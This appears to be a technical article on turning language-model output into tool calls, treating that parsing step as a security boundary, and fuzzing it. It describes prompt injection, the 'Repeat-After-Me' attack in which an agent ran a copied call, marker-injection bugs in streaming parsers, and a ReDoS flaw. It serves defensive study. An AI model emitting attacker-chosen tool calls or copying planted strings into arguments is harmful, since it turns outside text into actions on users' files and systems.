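# Fuzzing the conversion of language-model output into tool calls, and handling hostile output

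## How a model's text becomes a function call

Tool calling, or function calling, lets a language model use other software. The model produces only text, so when it requests a file or a database query, a surrounding program has to find the request in that text, run the matching function and return the result to the model. An AI agent is a language model that works through a task in this way, often over many rounds. The parsers and type converters that turn the text into a function call have bugs like other programs, and an outsider can sometimes influence the text they read. A standard way to find such bugs is fuzzing, running a program on many generated inputs and checking automatically for failures.

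### Tokens, tools and schemas

A language model works on tokens, which are words, pieces of words and punctuation marks, each with its own number. It takes a sequence of tokens, called the prompt, and extends it one token at a time. Most tokens stand for ordinary text, but a few special ones mark structure, such as the start of a message. According to OpenAI's format guide (2025), token 200012 in the gpt-oss models, which anyone can download and run, marks a request for a tool and signals the serving software to stop generating.

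A tool is a function that a model may ask software to run. It comes with a name, a description in plain language and a schema, a machine-readable description of its arguments and their types. Developers usually write the schema in JSON Schema, a vocabulary for describing data in the text format JSON. The running example from here on is a tool that writes a file, `write_file(path: string, text: string, overwrite: boolean)`:

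```json
{
  "name": "write_file",
  "description": "Write text to a file in the project folder.",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "path": {"type": "string"},
      "text": {"type": "string"},
      "overwrite": {"type": "boolean"}
    },
    "required": ["path", "text", "overwrite"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  }
}
```

The limit to the project folder appears only in the description. As far as the schema goes, any string will do as a path.

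The orchestrator is the software around the model that offers it tools, runs its tool calls and returns the results. *ToFu* (Ananto, Prevost-Avenel and colleagues, 2026) represents a tool call as *C* = ⟨*T*, {*a*₁ = *v*₁, …, *a*ₙ = *v*ₙ}⟩, where *T* is the tool and each *v*ᵢ is the value of its argument *a*ᵢ. The converter is the code that turns the model's output into *C*. It may be in the orchestrator, in the software that serves the model, or split between them.

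Many tools run in separate programs. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common interface to them, and a program that offers tools through it is an MCP server. An orchestrator sends the server a `tools/list` message to get the tools' names, descriptions and schemas, and a `tools/call` message with a name and arguments to run a tool. The Model Context Protocol (2026) project counted close to half a billion monthly downloads of its main software kits when it released the current version in July 2026. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports more than 950 MCP servers in the company's own directory.

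### One call through the loop

Suppose a user asks an agent to save the reminder "Call Ana at 3." in `notes/today.txt`, without replacing anything already there.

The orchestrator first sends the user's message together with the tool definitions. These become part of the prompt. OpenAI's *Function calling* guide explains that the definitions go into the system message, the block of standing instructions at the top of the prompt, in a syntax on which the company trained the model, and that they use up input tokens like any other text. For gpt-oss that syntax resembles the programming language TypeScript, so the model would receive `write_file` roughly as:

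```
// Write text to a file in the project folder.
type write_file = (_: {
  path: string,
  text: string,
  overwrite: boolean
}) => any;
```

The model then generates its answer. A model trained on a JSON format might produce a marker that opens a tool call, this object, and a closing marker:

```json
{"name": "write_file", "arguments": {"path": "notes/today.txt", "text": "Call Ana at 3.", "overwrite": false}}
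```

At this point nothing has happened to any file. Anthropic's *How tool use works* states, "The model never runs anything on its own." The output is a string of characters, so `false` is still text rather than a Boolean value.

Next the converter looks for the call. A parser for the DeepSeek-V3.1 model in vLLM, an open-source program for serving models on one's own machines, shows how simple this can be. If the marker that opens a block of calls is missing, the parser treats the whole output as ordinary text. If the marker is there, a regular expression (a search pattern) takes everything up to a separator as the tool's name and everything from the separator to the closing marker as its arguments. The parser passes on the arguments as raw text, without checking that they are valid JSON. Other code has to do that, and to turn the letters `false` into a Boolean value. The result is a typed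 call:

```
write_file(path = "notes/today.txt",    string
           text = "Call Ana at 3.",     string
           overwrite = false)           Boolean
```

The orchestrator should then check the call. It can confirm that it offered a tool of that name, compare the arguments with the schema, apply its permissions and ask the user for approval. Then the tool runs and creates the file.

Its result, perhaps "Wrote 14 characters", goes back into the conversation as another message, and the orchestrator sends the whole conversation to the model again. Results are usually text in whatever format the developer chose. Errors are returned the same way. Under MCP, a tool that rejects a badly formatted date should report this in its result, so that the model can correct the value and try again. Anthropic describes this process as a loop that continues as long as the model's answers end with a tool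 request. One answer may contain several calls, and OpenAI advises developers to assume this when writing their code.

### Is it a call, and should it run?

Between the model's text and the tool, software has to settle four separate matters. Each can go wrong while the others are fine.

| Question | An output for `write_file` that fails it |
|---|---|
| Is it a call? | The model quotes the JSON object above while explaining to the user how the tool works. |
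| Is it well formed? | The output breaks off in the middle of the path, with no closing quotation mark or brace. |
| Does it fit the schema? | `overwrite` holds the text "no", or the tool's name is `save_file`, which the orchestrator never offered. |
| Is it allowed and safe? | `path` is a perfectly good string that leads to a file outside the project folder. |

Software that serves models makes similar distinctions. *Build Tool-Calling Parsers in Rust with AI Agents* (NVIDIA, 2026), a post on parsers for NVIDIA's own serving system, treats a call that breaks off as a syntax error and a complete call to an unknown tool as a semantic error. The parser reports the second kind of call exactly as the model wrote it. The serving layer then checks whether the tool is available, whether the caller is authorized, and whether the call meets the schema and the policy on calls. A parser that quietly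 swapped in a similar tool name would hide what the model generated.

Guarantees about tool calls mostly concern their form. When a developer requires a call to a particular function, vLLM's *Tool Calling* documentation promises a "validly-parsable function call - not a high-quality one". vLLM enforces this with constrained decoding, which blocks every token that would break the schema. In automatic mode, the model decides whether to call a tool. Unless the developer has turned on strict checking for at least one tool, vLLM extracts calls in this mode from free text, and their arguments may be malformed or break the schema.

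A schema-valid call has the required fields and types, but its values may still be unsafe. MCP leaves safety checks to the server and client. Servers must validate all tool inputs and control access, and clients should ask the user to confirm sensitive operations. For `write_file`, someone has to write code that works out where a path actually leads.

### Who does the conversion

With a hosted API, where a company runs the model and developers reach it over the internet, the provider does most of the parsing, and the developer never sees the markers. Anthropic returns a block with the tool's name and a JSON object of arguments. OpenAI returns the name and a JSON string of arguments, which the developer's code must parse to get typed values. For a few tools, such as web search, Anthropic also runs the tool and the loop on its own servers.

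Anyone who serves a model on their own machines must also supply the converter. vLLM has a setting that selects a parser by name, and Red Hat's *Tool call parser type reference* tells operators of its inference server to choose the parser that matches their model's output format.

Agent frameworks, such as LangGraph, CrewAI and AutoGen, are libraries for building orchestrators. They generally work after a model's text has been parsed, taking structured calls from an API and passing them to the right function. Some also parse raw model output. Hamr, a small agent project, has its own parsers for the model families that vLLM supports because, according to its *Tool-Call Parsing* page, local models often do not produce clean calls in OpenAI's format.

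A single call can go through several conversions. For a self-hosted model with an MCP server, the serving software extracts the call from text and writes it as JSON, the orchestrator parses that JSON and writes a new message, and the MCP server parses the message and may convert the values again. Different people wrote these programs, often in different languages, so the programs may interpret an unusual input differently. Since July 2026, MCP requests over HTTP carry the tool's name in a header as well as in the body, so that network gateways can route and authorize a call without reading the body.

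### Why every model family needs its own parser

The JSON above is one of several notations. Other models write each argument between tags, as in this simplified version:

```xml
<call tool="write_file">
  <arg name="path">notes/today.txt</arg>
  <arg name="text">Call Ana at 3.</arg>
  <arg name="overwrite">false</arg>
</call>
```

Others write a list of calls in the style of the programming language Python:

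```python
[write_file(path='notes/today.txt', text='Call Ana at 3.', overwrite=False)]
```

All three express the same request, but a parser needs different rules for each. In JSON, the missing quotation marks show that `false` is a Boolean. In the XML-like version, nothing distinguishes the Boolean from the word, so the converter has to consult the schema. Python writes the value as `False`. A string ends with a double quotation mark in the JSON, a single one in this Python, and a closing tag in the XML-like version. A reminder that contains one of these needs special treatment in one notation but not in another.

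A model learns its notation in training, so the people who serve it cannot simply pick a tidier one. OpenAI warns that gpt-oss will not work correctly without its own format. The vLLM version with the DeepSeek parser described above had 23 separate tool parsers. Formats change even within a model family. NVIDIA's *Tool Call Parsing (Dynamo)* lists four parsers for DeepSeek models from V3 to V4, with special Unicode markers in one version and tags in another. The Olmo 3 models write Python-like calls inside XML tags, and vLLM's parser for them accepts both the Python and the JSON spelling of true and false. The Llama 3.2 models produce no marker before or after a Python-like call.

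Much of this code is new, and developers add to it whenever a new model appears. In *AI Security is a LangSec Problem*, von Hippel and Miyazono point out that such parsers "cannot assume anything" about the model output. The parsers also have to work while the text is still arriving, since many applications show the answer as the model writes it.

### Fuzzing

A fuzzer usually begins with sample inputs, called seeds, and alters them to make new ones. The JSON call above would be a reasonable seed for testing a converter. The alterations, called mutations, might include deleting a brace, repeating a field or replacing `false` with a very long number. A small piece of code called a test harness passes each new input to the program under test. This process repeats thousands of times or more.

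Blind mutation wastes most of this effort, so many fuzzers use coverage feedback, recording which parts of the program's code each input reaches. *libFuzzer*, a widely used fuzzer from the LLVM compiler project, saves any mutated input that reaches new code and mutates it further. It can therefore reach deeper into a program step by step without a description of the input format. LLVM recommends starting from a varied set of valid and invalid inputs.

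*Dissecting Software Graphs* (2026) notes that coverage reflects only the code reached with a particular set of inputs and a particular configuration. If a server is set up for one model's parser, even a long fuzzing run on it provides no information about the other 22 parsers.

*Adaptive and AI-Augmented Security Testing* (2026), a survey, reports that programs that read formats such as JSON reject most randomly mutated inputs during parsing, before the more interesting code runs. Superion, a fuzzer the survey covers, avoids this by parsing a seed input into a tree and replacing, inserting or deleting whole branches, so that the result is still valid. Another method generates inputs from the format's specification, without a seed. *Multi-target Coverage-based Greybox Fuzzing* (2026) cites a study of the PNG image format in which mutation reached on average only 24% of the code coverage that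 generation from the specification achieved. That figure may not apply to tool calls, but parsing is an obstacle there too. A fuzzer can also skip the text and pass typed values directly to the code, as Rust Fuzz's *Structure-Aware Fuzzing* guide shows for Rust programs.

Which kind of input to use depends on the code under test. A converter has to handle broken text, so its tests need malformed inputs. A tool behind a strict schema check would never receive them, so tests of `write_file` itself need two proper strings and a Boolean, with the hostile content inside the strings.

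The fuzzer also needs an oracle, the rule that decides whether a run has failed. The simplest oracle checks for a crash, but it misses many failures here. Ananto and colleagues give the example of a file tool that opens a file outside its permitted folder and returns normally. A useful oracle for `write_file` would check after every call that no file outside the project folder had changed. For a converter, one option is differential testing, which gives two programs the same input and checks whether their outputs differ.

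When a flaw becomes public, it often receives a CVE (Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures) number, which identifies that flaw in a particular product. CWE (Common Weakness Enumeration) is a catalogue of types of weakness, such as path traversal, in which a crafted path leads a program to a file outside its permitted folder.

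## Why the conversion is a security boundary

A security boundary is a point where data from a less trusted source reaches code that has more power than the source. The part of a web server that reads incoming requests is on such a boundary, because anyone can send a request and the server acts on it with its own rights. The case for treating the converter the same way goes as follows:

1. Outsiders can influence what a model writes.
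2. The converter turns some of that writing into tool calls, which other software then runs.
3. Tools run with the permissions of the orchestrator or of the machine that hosts them, and outsiders usually lack those permissions.
4. The converter and the tools must therefore be safe on every output the model could produce, including one that an attacker has chosen.

Tool results become part of the model's prompt, and anything in the prompt can affect what the model writes next. So whoever wrote a web page that an agent reads has written part of the agent's prompt. Indirect prompt injection exploits this by placing instructions in content that a model reads while doing someone else's task. An attacker's text can also reach a tool call's arguments without the model obeying any instructions, for example when the model copies a title or file name from the page.

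Ananto and colleagues note that an MCP server runs with the privileges of whoever started it, usually the user's account. In that case, `write_file` can write anywhere the user can, regardless of which folder its description mentions. Security engineers call a program a confused deputy when someone who lacks certain rights gets it to misuse the rights it holds. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) lists this among the risks of tool-using models, whose harmful outputs may become emails, payments, code changes or shell commands.

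The conversion code should be safe on every output, even though most are harmless, because an attacker who writes part of the prompt can make a rare output likely. Unless constrained decoding rules a string out, developers can't assume that the model will never produce it.

### Hostile output in both directions

Hostile output is text that an attacker has chosen or influenced, whether it comes from a model, tool, file or web page. The hostile-output problem is how to keep the software around a model safe when any text it reads may be hostile.

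On the way out, from model to tool, the requirement can be written down. Let *f* be the converter, which maps a string to a list of tool calls or an error, and let *P* be the set of effects that the operator permits. Then for every string *s*:

- *f*(*s*) finishes within fixed limits on time and memory and changes nothing else;
- running the calls in *f*(*s*), after any checks, has only effects in *P*.

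Ordinary software tests usually cover something much weaker, the strings that a helpful model tends to write.

The tool's result passes through more code before the model sees it. The orchestrator may decode JSON, extract text from a PDF or show part of the result in a terminal, and a crafted result can exploit a flaw in any of these steps. A hostile result in one round can also lead to a hostile tool call in the next. The *Lifecycle* survey recommends treating tool outputs as untrusted, with the same isolation and clean-up as web content.

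Much of the outgoing half is already known in application security as improper output handling. OWASP, a non-profit that publishes lists of common software risks, included it in its 2025 list for language-model applications. *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* (2025) covers insufficient checking of model output before other components receive it, such as when output goes straight into a system shell, a database query or a file path. Because prompts can control the output, OWASP compares the flaw to giving users indirect access to extra functions, and it advises developers to treat the model "as any other user". Prompt injection is a separate category, which still tops OWASP's latest list according to *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (Coker, 2026). The two often occur together, when injection supplies the text and poor output handling lets it do harm.

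In their threat model, Ananto and colleagues assume that an attacker can influence user prompts, retrieved content and the outputs of other tools, and that any schema-valid argument may be hostile. They trust the orchestrator to pass schema-valid calls on correctly. This is reasonable in a study of tools, but anyone testing the converter can't rely on that assumption, because they are testing whether the converter handles hostile text correctly.

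### The Repeat-After-Me attack

Ananto and colleagues demonstrate the problem using an attack they call Repeat-After-Me. The attacker chooses a tool and all its arguments, writes out the complete call in the format that the orchestrator recognizes, and asks the model to repeat it word for word. If the model does, the orchestrator finds a tool call in the output and runs it, even though the model only copied text.

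The one published transcript comes from an agent built with LangGraph and Llama 3.1 8B, a small model running locally through Ollama. The agent had two tools with alarming names, one for launching missiles, but both were stubs that did nothing but return a fixed list. The only safeguard was an instruction in the system message to decline dangerous requests.

On the first attempt, the model refused but still printed the requested call at the end of its refusal. Nothing ran, because the software did not recognize a call inside other text. The attacker then described the request as hypothetical and asked for only the quoted string. The model returned an empty message with a structured call containing exactly the attacker's number, and LangGraph ran it immediately. The model refused again only after the tool had returned, as though no call had taken place. The empty message suggests that Ollama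 had removed the call from the text and converted it before LangGraph received anything.

The attack required the attacker to know the call format and the model to reproduce the call exactly, in this setup with no other text around it. It also required that no permission check or human approval stand between the conversion and the tool. Ananto and colleagues say they reproduced the behavior in six frameworks: LangGraph, Microsoft Agent Framework, Google's Agent Development Kit, AutoGen, Strands and CrewAI. They report no success rates and show no transcripts for the other five, so it is unclear how often the attack works or how larger, newer models respond.

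The attacker in the transcript is also the user, who may well have been entitled to use the tools. Someone who tricks an agent into doing what they could have asked for openly has gained little, except where the operator meant to forbid it. The more general lesson is about what a tool call contains. Take this one:

```
write_file(path = "notes/today.txt", text = "", overwrite = true)
```

The user may have asked the agent to clear today's notes, or the model may have copied the call from a web page. Either way, the call contains a tool name and three values of the right types, with no field for who requested it. A check that looks only at the call cannot distinguish these cases, so matching the schema is no evidence of who made the request.

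In *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security*, Siu, He and colleagues (2026) define security so that the same action can be legitimate or a violation depending on whose instruction led to it. One of their four security properties, source authorization, requires commands to come from authenticated sources. Some defenses try to supply the missing information about origin by recording where each piece of data came from and restricting what untrusted data can affect. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby (2026) built an agent this way, with machine-checked proofs for the program that runs it. The agent resisted attack in all but two of 1,296 attacked runs on a banking benchmark. Garby also warns that such tracking is easy to get wrong where data enters or leaves the tracked system. The converter is one of those places, because it turns text into new values that must keep the record of where they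 came from.

### Recognize the whole input first

Language-theoretic security, or LangSec, is a school of research about input handling. LangSec's *The Tower of Babel* proposes treating a program's valid inputs as a formal language, an exactly defined set of strings, and the input-handling code as a recognizer that accepts only those strings. *The Seven Turrets of Babel* (Momot, Bratus and colleagues, 2016) turns this into a working rule that developers should define the input with a grammar, keep the grammar as simple as possible, and finish checking the whole input before using any of it.

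A grammar for the arguments of `write_file` might look like this. For brevity, it fixes the order of the fields and allows no spaces between them.

```
arguments = '{"path":' path ',"text":' string ',"overwrite":' boolean '}'
path      = '"' name ( "/" name )* '"'
name      = ( letter | digit | "_" | "-" )+ ( "." ( letter | digit )+ )?
boolean   = "true" | "false"
```

Here `string` stands for any JSON string. The path `notes/today.txt` fits, but a path that starts with a slash or uses `..` to reach a parent folder does not, because every name must begin with a letter, digit, underscore or hyphen. The schema would accept all three paths.

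Momot and colleagues call the opposite habit shotgun parsing, in which input checks are scattered through the code that acts on the input. A converter may divide its checks between several programs, as long as they all finish before any tool runs. If an orchestrator instead starts writing `text` to the file while the model is still producing it, it may discover that the output is cut off or contains a bad path only after the file has changed. Momot and colleagues describe a similar path traversal flaw in the web framework Rails. Its developers had not specified what a valid path was, so the operating system did the checking without any information about the application's rules.

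The advice to keep grammars simple has a mathematical basis. Momot and colleagues recommend staying within the deterministic context-free languages, which a program can read from left to right with a single stack and no guessing. An algorithm can decide whether two grammars for such languages accept the same strings, which is impossible for context-free grammars in general. This matters for tool calls because a call can get past a check when two programs parse it differently. JSON can stay within the class if its fields do not depend on one another in complicated ways. *CBCL* (O'Connor, 2026), a language for messages between agents, enforces the limit even when agents add their own vocabulary. However, it would have to replace existing formats that models have learned in training.

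Momot and colleagues reviewed 47 vulnerabilities reported between January 2015 and June 2016 in OpenSSL, a widely used cryptography library, and judged that LangSec design would have avoided 35. They attributed 13 to shotgun parsing and 11 to processing input that the program should have rejected. These researchers advocate LangSec and studied only one library, written in C, and a converter written in Python will have a different mix of bugs. Still, the count suggests that even in security software, much of the danger is in reading input.

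A grammar also can't guarantee that `write_file` stays inside the project folder. If the folder `notes` is a symbolic link, an entry that points to another place on the disk, a path through it could fit the grammar and still lead outside the project. Only code that checks the actual file system can detect this.

### LangSec and language models

von Hippel and Miyazono brought this approach to language models in 2025. They consider tool calls together with structured outputs, in which a model has to return data in a fixed shape such as a JSON object. In their account, developers extend the parsers for such output bit by bit as customers ask for features, with little thought about how complex the accepted language is becoming. The parsers typically run alongside the main application without isolation, and so do the tools. An attacker who can steer the model's output can therefore try to exploit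 a parser bug on the application's own server. Parsers for model output also have an unusual duty, which is to produce a clear error message on failure so that the application can ask the model to repair its answer.

Maitai, a company that hosts and routes language models, analyzed its customers' traffic for the paper to measure how common these features were. About 21.2% of requests involved structured outputs and 32.7% involved tool calls, with little overlap, so roughly half of the traffic went through one kind of parser or the other. The figures describe one provider in early 2025, and the paper doesn't give the number of requests or the exact period.

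Von Hippel and Miyazono's survey is much weaker evidence. They reached five founders of startups backed by the investor Y Combinator, through its private social network. Four used structured outputs, one had built a custom parser, and four expressed security concerns. Von Hippel and Miyazono call these results anecdotal, and the exploits they list for tools are also theoretical. Their case therefore depends mainly on the reasoning about untrusted input, though some converters have since turned out to run model output as program code.

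### Training lowers the odds

Developers have had real success training models to ignore injected instructions. Anthropic reported in June 2026 that its model Mythos 5 had the best result yet on a prompt injection benchmark from the company Gray Swan. If models resist nearly every attack, strict checks on their output might seem unnecessary.

An attacker can often try again. If each attempt succeeds independently with probability *p*, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ. When *p* is one in a thousand, a thousand attempts give about a 63% chance of success. Real attempts are not independent, as VentureBeat's account of tests on Claude Opus 4.6, an older Anthropic model, shows. When that model operated a graphical interface without extra safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and 78.6% of attacks had succeeded by the 200th attempt. Independent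 attempts would have reached 78.6% after about eight tries. Some attacks evidently fail however often the attacker repeats them, but many eventually succeed. Even with safeguards, 57.1% had succeeded by the 200th attempt.

In a restricted coding environment, the same model resisted all 200 attempts. If the attempts were independent, that result is still statistically compatible with a success rate of up to about 1.5% per attempt. It also applies only to the attacks that the testers used. Zorz (2026), in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection thousands*, reports research in which training on more injection attacks left agents easier to hijack, and suggests that large collections of attacks may mostly repeat the same one.

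The training is still useful. It reduces how often hostile calls reach the tools, and it may be the main defense for tools whose legitimate use is itself dangerous, such as one that sends email. But a correct path check in `write_file` works on every attempt, whichever model wrote the path. It also catches harmful paths that the model produces by mistake.

### Whose machine is at risk

Another objection is that users who make an agent misbehave harm only themselves. This is sometimes true. Someone who runs an agent on a laptop and types a prompt that makes it overwrite a private file could have overwritten the file directly. Whether a flaw matters for security depends on who chooses the text and whose permissions the code has:

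| Who chooses the text | Where the vulnerable code runs | What the attacker can gain |
|---|---|---|
| The user | The user's own laptop | Usually nothing new |
| One customer | A model server that many customers share | A crash that affects everyone, or access to other customers' data |
| The author of a web page | The laptop of a user whose agent reads the page | The user's files and accounts |
| The operator of a remote MCP server | The orchestrator that reads its results | Whatever the orchestrator can reach |

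On a shared server, the converter may process text from unrelated users, and one request that crashes it can interrupt service for all of them. An ordinary customer can carry out an attack like Repeat-After-Me without a third party, because they can ask the model for almost any string. On a laptop, the danger comes from the content the agent reads. The *Lifecycle* survey points out that web pages, code repositories, support tickets, emails and PDFs can contain instructions meant for the agent rather than the human reader. The objection therefore applies only to an agent with one user, no outside content and no remote tools, which excludes browsing, email and most work on shared code.

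### Assume a malicious model, or test the whole agent?

If any model output may be hostile, a tester could leave the model out and feed hostile text straight to the code that processes it. The undated essay *Prompt Fuzzing is Pointless* argues for this with a demonstration by Garrett Galloway, in which a server imitates OpenAI's API. A client asks the server for 2 + 2 and offers a calculator tool, and the server answers with a tool call whose argument is a Python command instead of a sum. The client runs the argument as Python code, and the command creates a file. No language model takes part, and the flaw is entirely in the client.

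This is a sound way to find bugs. It is repeatable, needs few resources, and does not depend on how persuasive the tester's prompts are. Ananto and colleagues take the same position for tools. They treat every schema-valid argument as potentially hostile and test the tool's code against it, leaving for later how an attacker would deliver it. Their fuzzer therefore calls tools directly.

The essay overstates its remedy when it says that a strict grammar, enforced through constrained decoding, makes a model "incapable of misbehaving". That may be nearly true for a calculator, since a grammar of numbers and operators excludes Python commands, but a harmful `write_file` request can have exactly the same form as a useful one. Constrained decoding would not have stopped the demonstration either, because the fake server controlled the decoding. The client had to check the argument itself, which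 the essay also recommends. The essay places the trust boundary after parsing and validation. That is right for the values, but the parser is also exposed because it has to process the raw text first.

The case for testing the whole agent is that a flaw matters only if an attacker can reach it. An API may re-encode the arguments and remove the characters an exploit depends on, or an approval step may stop the call. A tester who ignores these steps can produce a long list of flaws without knowing which to fix first. Agent-level fuzzers look for reachable flaws by changing prompts or content until a hostile value arrives at a tool.

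Reachability is easy to underestimate, however. In *Oops!... I Parsed It Again*, Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz (2026) found that Qwen3.8-27B never followed an instruction planted in a document in 25 trials, but in 19 of 25 it copied a planted string into a tool call's arguments. A test that counted only obeyed instructions would have rated it safe. A failed attack is also weak evidence about the next model, and operators change models often while keeping the same tools. It therefore makes sense to test the converter and tools directly on hostile input, then use whole-agent tests to rank the resulting flaws by urgency. Flaws that no agent test has reached should get lower priority but should not be dismissed.

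## Finding the call in the model's output

A model with tools can produce reasoning, text for the user and tool calls in a single answer, which arrives as one stream of tokens. The parser has to divide this stream into parts, label them and keep them in order. In NVIDIA's serving system, a separate adapter then converts the labeled parts to the API's format.

### Markers

The parser finds the boundaries by looking for markers that the model learned in training. *Better Models* (Ronacher, 2026), an article about faulty tool calls, describes this as "rather crude in-band signalling", meaning that the signals travel in the same channel as the content. Telephone networks once used audible tones this way, and callers who could reproduce them could make free calls.

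Some markers are special tokens, such as token 200012 in gpt-oss. A parser that reads token numbers can recognize these exactly. If the model spells out the same characters in a sentence, they usually come out as several ordinary tokens with different numbers. Both decode to the same string, so a parser that reads text can't tell them apart.

Decoding can also delete a marker, because serving software often leaves special tokens out of the text. vLLM's parser for GLM-4 models sets an option that keeps them. The GLM-4 markers are not registered as special tokens, but according to a comment in the code, newer versions of the decoding library may behave differently.

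### Reading the output in pieces

When an application shows an answer as the model writes it, the parser receives the text in pieces and has to pass most of it on before the model has written the rest. The GLM-4 parser used to hold each string argument until it was complete. This could delay a 4,000-character file by several seconds, so the parser now passes strings on as they arrive.

To do this, it keeps a buffer of unprocessed text and records whether it is inside a call, which tool the call names, which argument it is reading, whether it is inside a string, and which argument names have already appeared. The table shows the method applied to `write_file`, in the simplified XML-like notation.

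| New piece | What the parser can pass on | What it holds back |
|---|---|---|
| `Saving it now. <ca` | The visible text `Saving it now. ` | `<ca` |
| `ll tool="write_file">` | The tool's name | Nothing |
| `<arg name="path">notes/today.txt</arg>` | `{"path":"notes/today.txt"` | Nothing |
| `<arg name="text">Call Ana at 3.</a` | `,"text":"Call Ana at 3.` | `</a` |
| `rg>` | `"` | Nothing |
| `<arg name="overwrite">false</arg></call>` | `,"overwrite":false}` | Nothing |

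The first piece ends in the middle of a marker, so the parser has to hold `<ca` until more text arrives. If it released `<ca` as visible text, it would not recognize the marker when the second piece came, and the user would see a broken call instead of getting a file. If the next piece were `t>`, making the harmless word `<cat>`, the parser would release the held text. The same problem occurs at the end of the `text` argument, where releasing `</a` too early would put those three characters into the file.

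The code that calls the parser has to handle the parser's results correctly. Modular, which makes another serving system, defines two results for a parser that has nothing to pass on. One means that the parser needs more tokens, for example because it may be holding the start of a marker. The other means that the parser is inside a tool call, and the caller must keep the raw token out of the visible text.

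Streaming also makes mistakes harder to undo. When the GLM-4 parser reaches the end of a call, it checks whether the arguments it has passed on form valid JSON. If they don't, it can only log a warning, because it has already sent them.

A correct parser gives the same result however the stream is divided. If the pieces are *p*₁, …, *p*ₖ, it should find the same calls in them as in the joined string *p*₁*p*₂…*p*ₖ. Several of the bugs below break this rule.

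### A closing marker inside the text

Suppose the user wants to save a note about the notation itself:

```xml
<arg name="text">End every value with </arg> or it fails.</arg>
```

The GLM-4 parser ends a string at the first closing marker and skips the rest, so the file would contain only "End every value with ". JSON avoids this problem by putting a backslash before any quotation mark inside a string. The GLM-4 parser has no such escaping rule for its markers.

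An attacker can use the skipped part. If the model copies content from a web page into the `text` argument, that content could close the argument early and open another, such as `overwrite` set to `true`. The model's own `overwrite`, set to `false`, would follow later in the same call.

Which value wins depends on whether the application streams the answer. vLLM has separate code for streamed and complete answers, and the two versions of the GLM-4 parser disagree on several inputs:

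| Model output | Streamed answer | Complete answer |
|---|---|---|
| `overwrite` appears twice, first `true`, then `false` | `true` | `false` |
| The marker that closes the whole call appears inside `text` | The call arrives intact | The call contains only `path` |
| The output stops in the middle of `text` | The tool's name, `path` and part of `text` have already gone out | There is no call, and the raw markup becomes visible text |

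A schema check would reject the call that contains only `path`, because the other two arguments are required, but it would accept either value of `overwrite`. A developer who tests with complete answers could therefore see the file protected every time, while users who receive streamed answers lose the file.

Other parsers have similar trouble. NVIDIA's *Tool Calling Probe Snapshot for Dynamo 1.2* (2026) reports tests of seven models on Dynamo, the company's serving system, with 36 to 48 requests per model. One test required an argument containing text that resembled a marker. The text did not arrive intact with GLM 5.1, MiniMax 2.7 or Gemma 4 31B, with or without streaming. Dynamo's development version still had the fault in June 2026.

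With Gemma, the argument was a database query, and the parser cut it off just before the marker-like text. A shortened query may still be valid, and a delete query that has lost its last condition deletes too many rows. DeepSeek V4 Pro passed all 46 of its tests, so the loss seems avoidable.

### Where the reasoning ends

A model may draft a tool call in its reasoning and then abandon it. The parser may let that draft run if it marks the end of the reasoning too early, or miss a real call if it marks the end too late.

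The second error occurred with the Kimi K2.6 model in Dynamo 1.2. Of 36 test requests, 18 failed at the parser or API boundary. In some, tool-call markup appeared in the reasoning and the application received no structured call, and in others part of the final answer went to the wrong place. These failures had been fixed in the development version by the time of the report.

Finding the call is difficult partly because different programs may look for the same boundary. In *Streaming Tokens and Tools* (Kosec, Dhanani and colleagues, 2026), NVIDIA engineers describe a setup in which one parser handled a model's reasoning and another handled its tool calls. The serving software had already separated the reasoning, but the code that prepared the API response searched for the boundary again. After the fix, only one component finds the boundary, and later components accept its result.

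Poolside's *Laguna M.1/XS.2 Technical Report* (2026) describes a problem with how vLLM's parser for DeepSeek-V3 checked whether the reasoning in a streamed answer had ended. The parser searched the entire prompt for the marker that closes reasoning. Poolside's coding models keep their earlier reasoning in the prompt, so the parser could find an old marker and treat new reasoning as finished. Poolside contributed a parser that searches only the current turn.

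According to the developer notes for Dynamo, some parsers add an opening reasoning marker without checking whether the model is reasoning. If the setting is wrong, this marker ends up in the JSON that the tool-call parser receives.

### Several tokens in one piece

Poolside also found that some of vLLM's streaming parsers assumed that every piece contained exactly one token. With one token per piece, a marker always arrives alone, so the parser never has to handle the end of one part and the start of the next in the same piece.

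In real use, a piece can contain several tokens. In speculative decoding, a fast method proposes a few tokens and the main model accepts them in one step. vLLM also merges pieces when the model produces text faster than the next program collects it. If a piece contained a marker followed by other text, the parsers silently dropped the text after the marker. In a call to `write_file`, this could remove the start of the tool's name or its first argument. Poolside saw invalid tool calls as a result and contributed improved parsers to vLLM.

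This bug is hard to notice. The second cause depends on timing, so the same output might parse correctly on a quiet server and fail on a busy one. The symptoms also looked exactly like those of a model that had learned to use its markers badly, and Poolside writes that such failures were often invisible or at least under-reported. In *troubleshooting tool calls*, NVIDIA therefore asks people who report bugs to include the raw bytes of the stream. Its developers compare these with the parsed response to decide whether the model, the parser's settings or the parser itself caused the failure.

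### A search pattern that froze the server

Many parsers look for calls with a regular expression. A badly written expression can take so long to process a short string that the server stops responding. vLLM's parser for Python-style calls had this flaw, which became public in May 2025 as CVE-2025-48887.

In a regular expression, `+` means one or more repetitions of the item before it, so the pattern `(a+)+b` matches one or more groups, each of one or more letters `a`, followed by a `b`. The string `aaaa` has no `b`, so it can't match. But before giving up, many search programs try every way of dividing the letters into groups, starting with one group of four, then three and one, two and two, two and one and one, and so on. Going back to try another division after each dead end is called backtracking. Every gap between two letters may or may not separate two groups, so a string of *n* letters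 has 2ⁿ⁻¹ possible divisions, and each extra letter doubles the number.

vLLM's pattern had the same structure on a larger scale. It contained a repeated pattern for calls, inside which was a repeated pattern for arguments, and the value of each argument could be any run of characters. Such a run can include commas, equals signs and parentheses. The same stretch of text could therefore count as one long argument, several short ones or several calls. An attacker's string repeats a fragment that resembles the start of a call, without ever completing a valid list.

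The advisory, which Corgea's *vLLM has a Regular Expression Denial of Service (ReDoS, Exponential Complexity) Vulnerability* reproduces, gives these timings for strings that don't match:

| Characters | Seconds |
|---|---|
| 38 | 0.001 |
| 54 | 0.025 |
| 70 | 0.52 |
| 86 | 13.3 |
| 102 | 319 |

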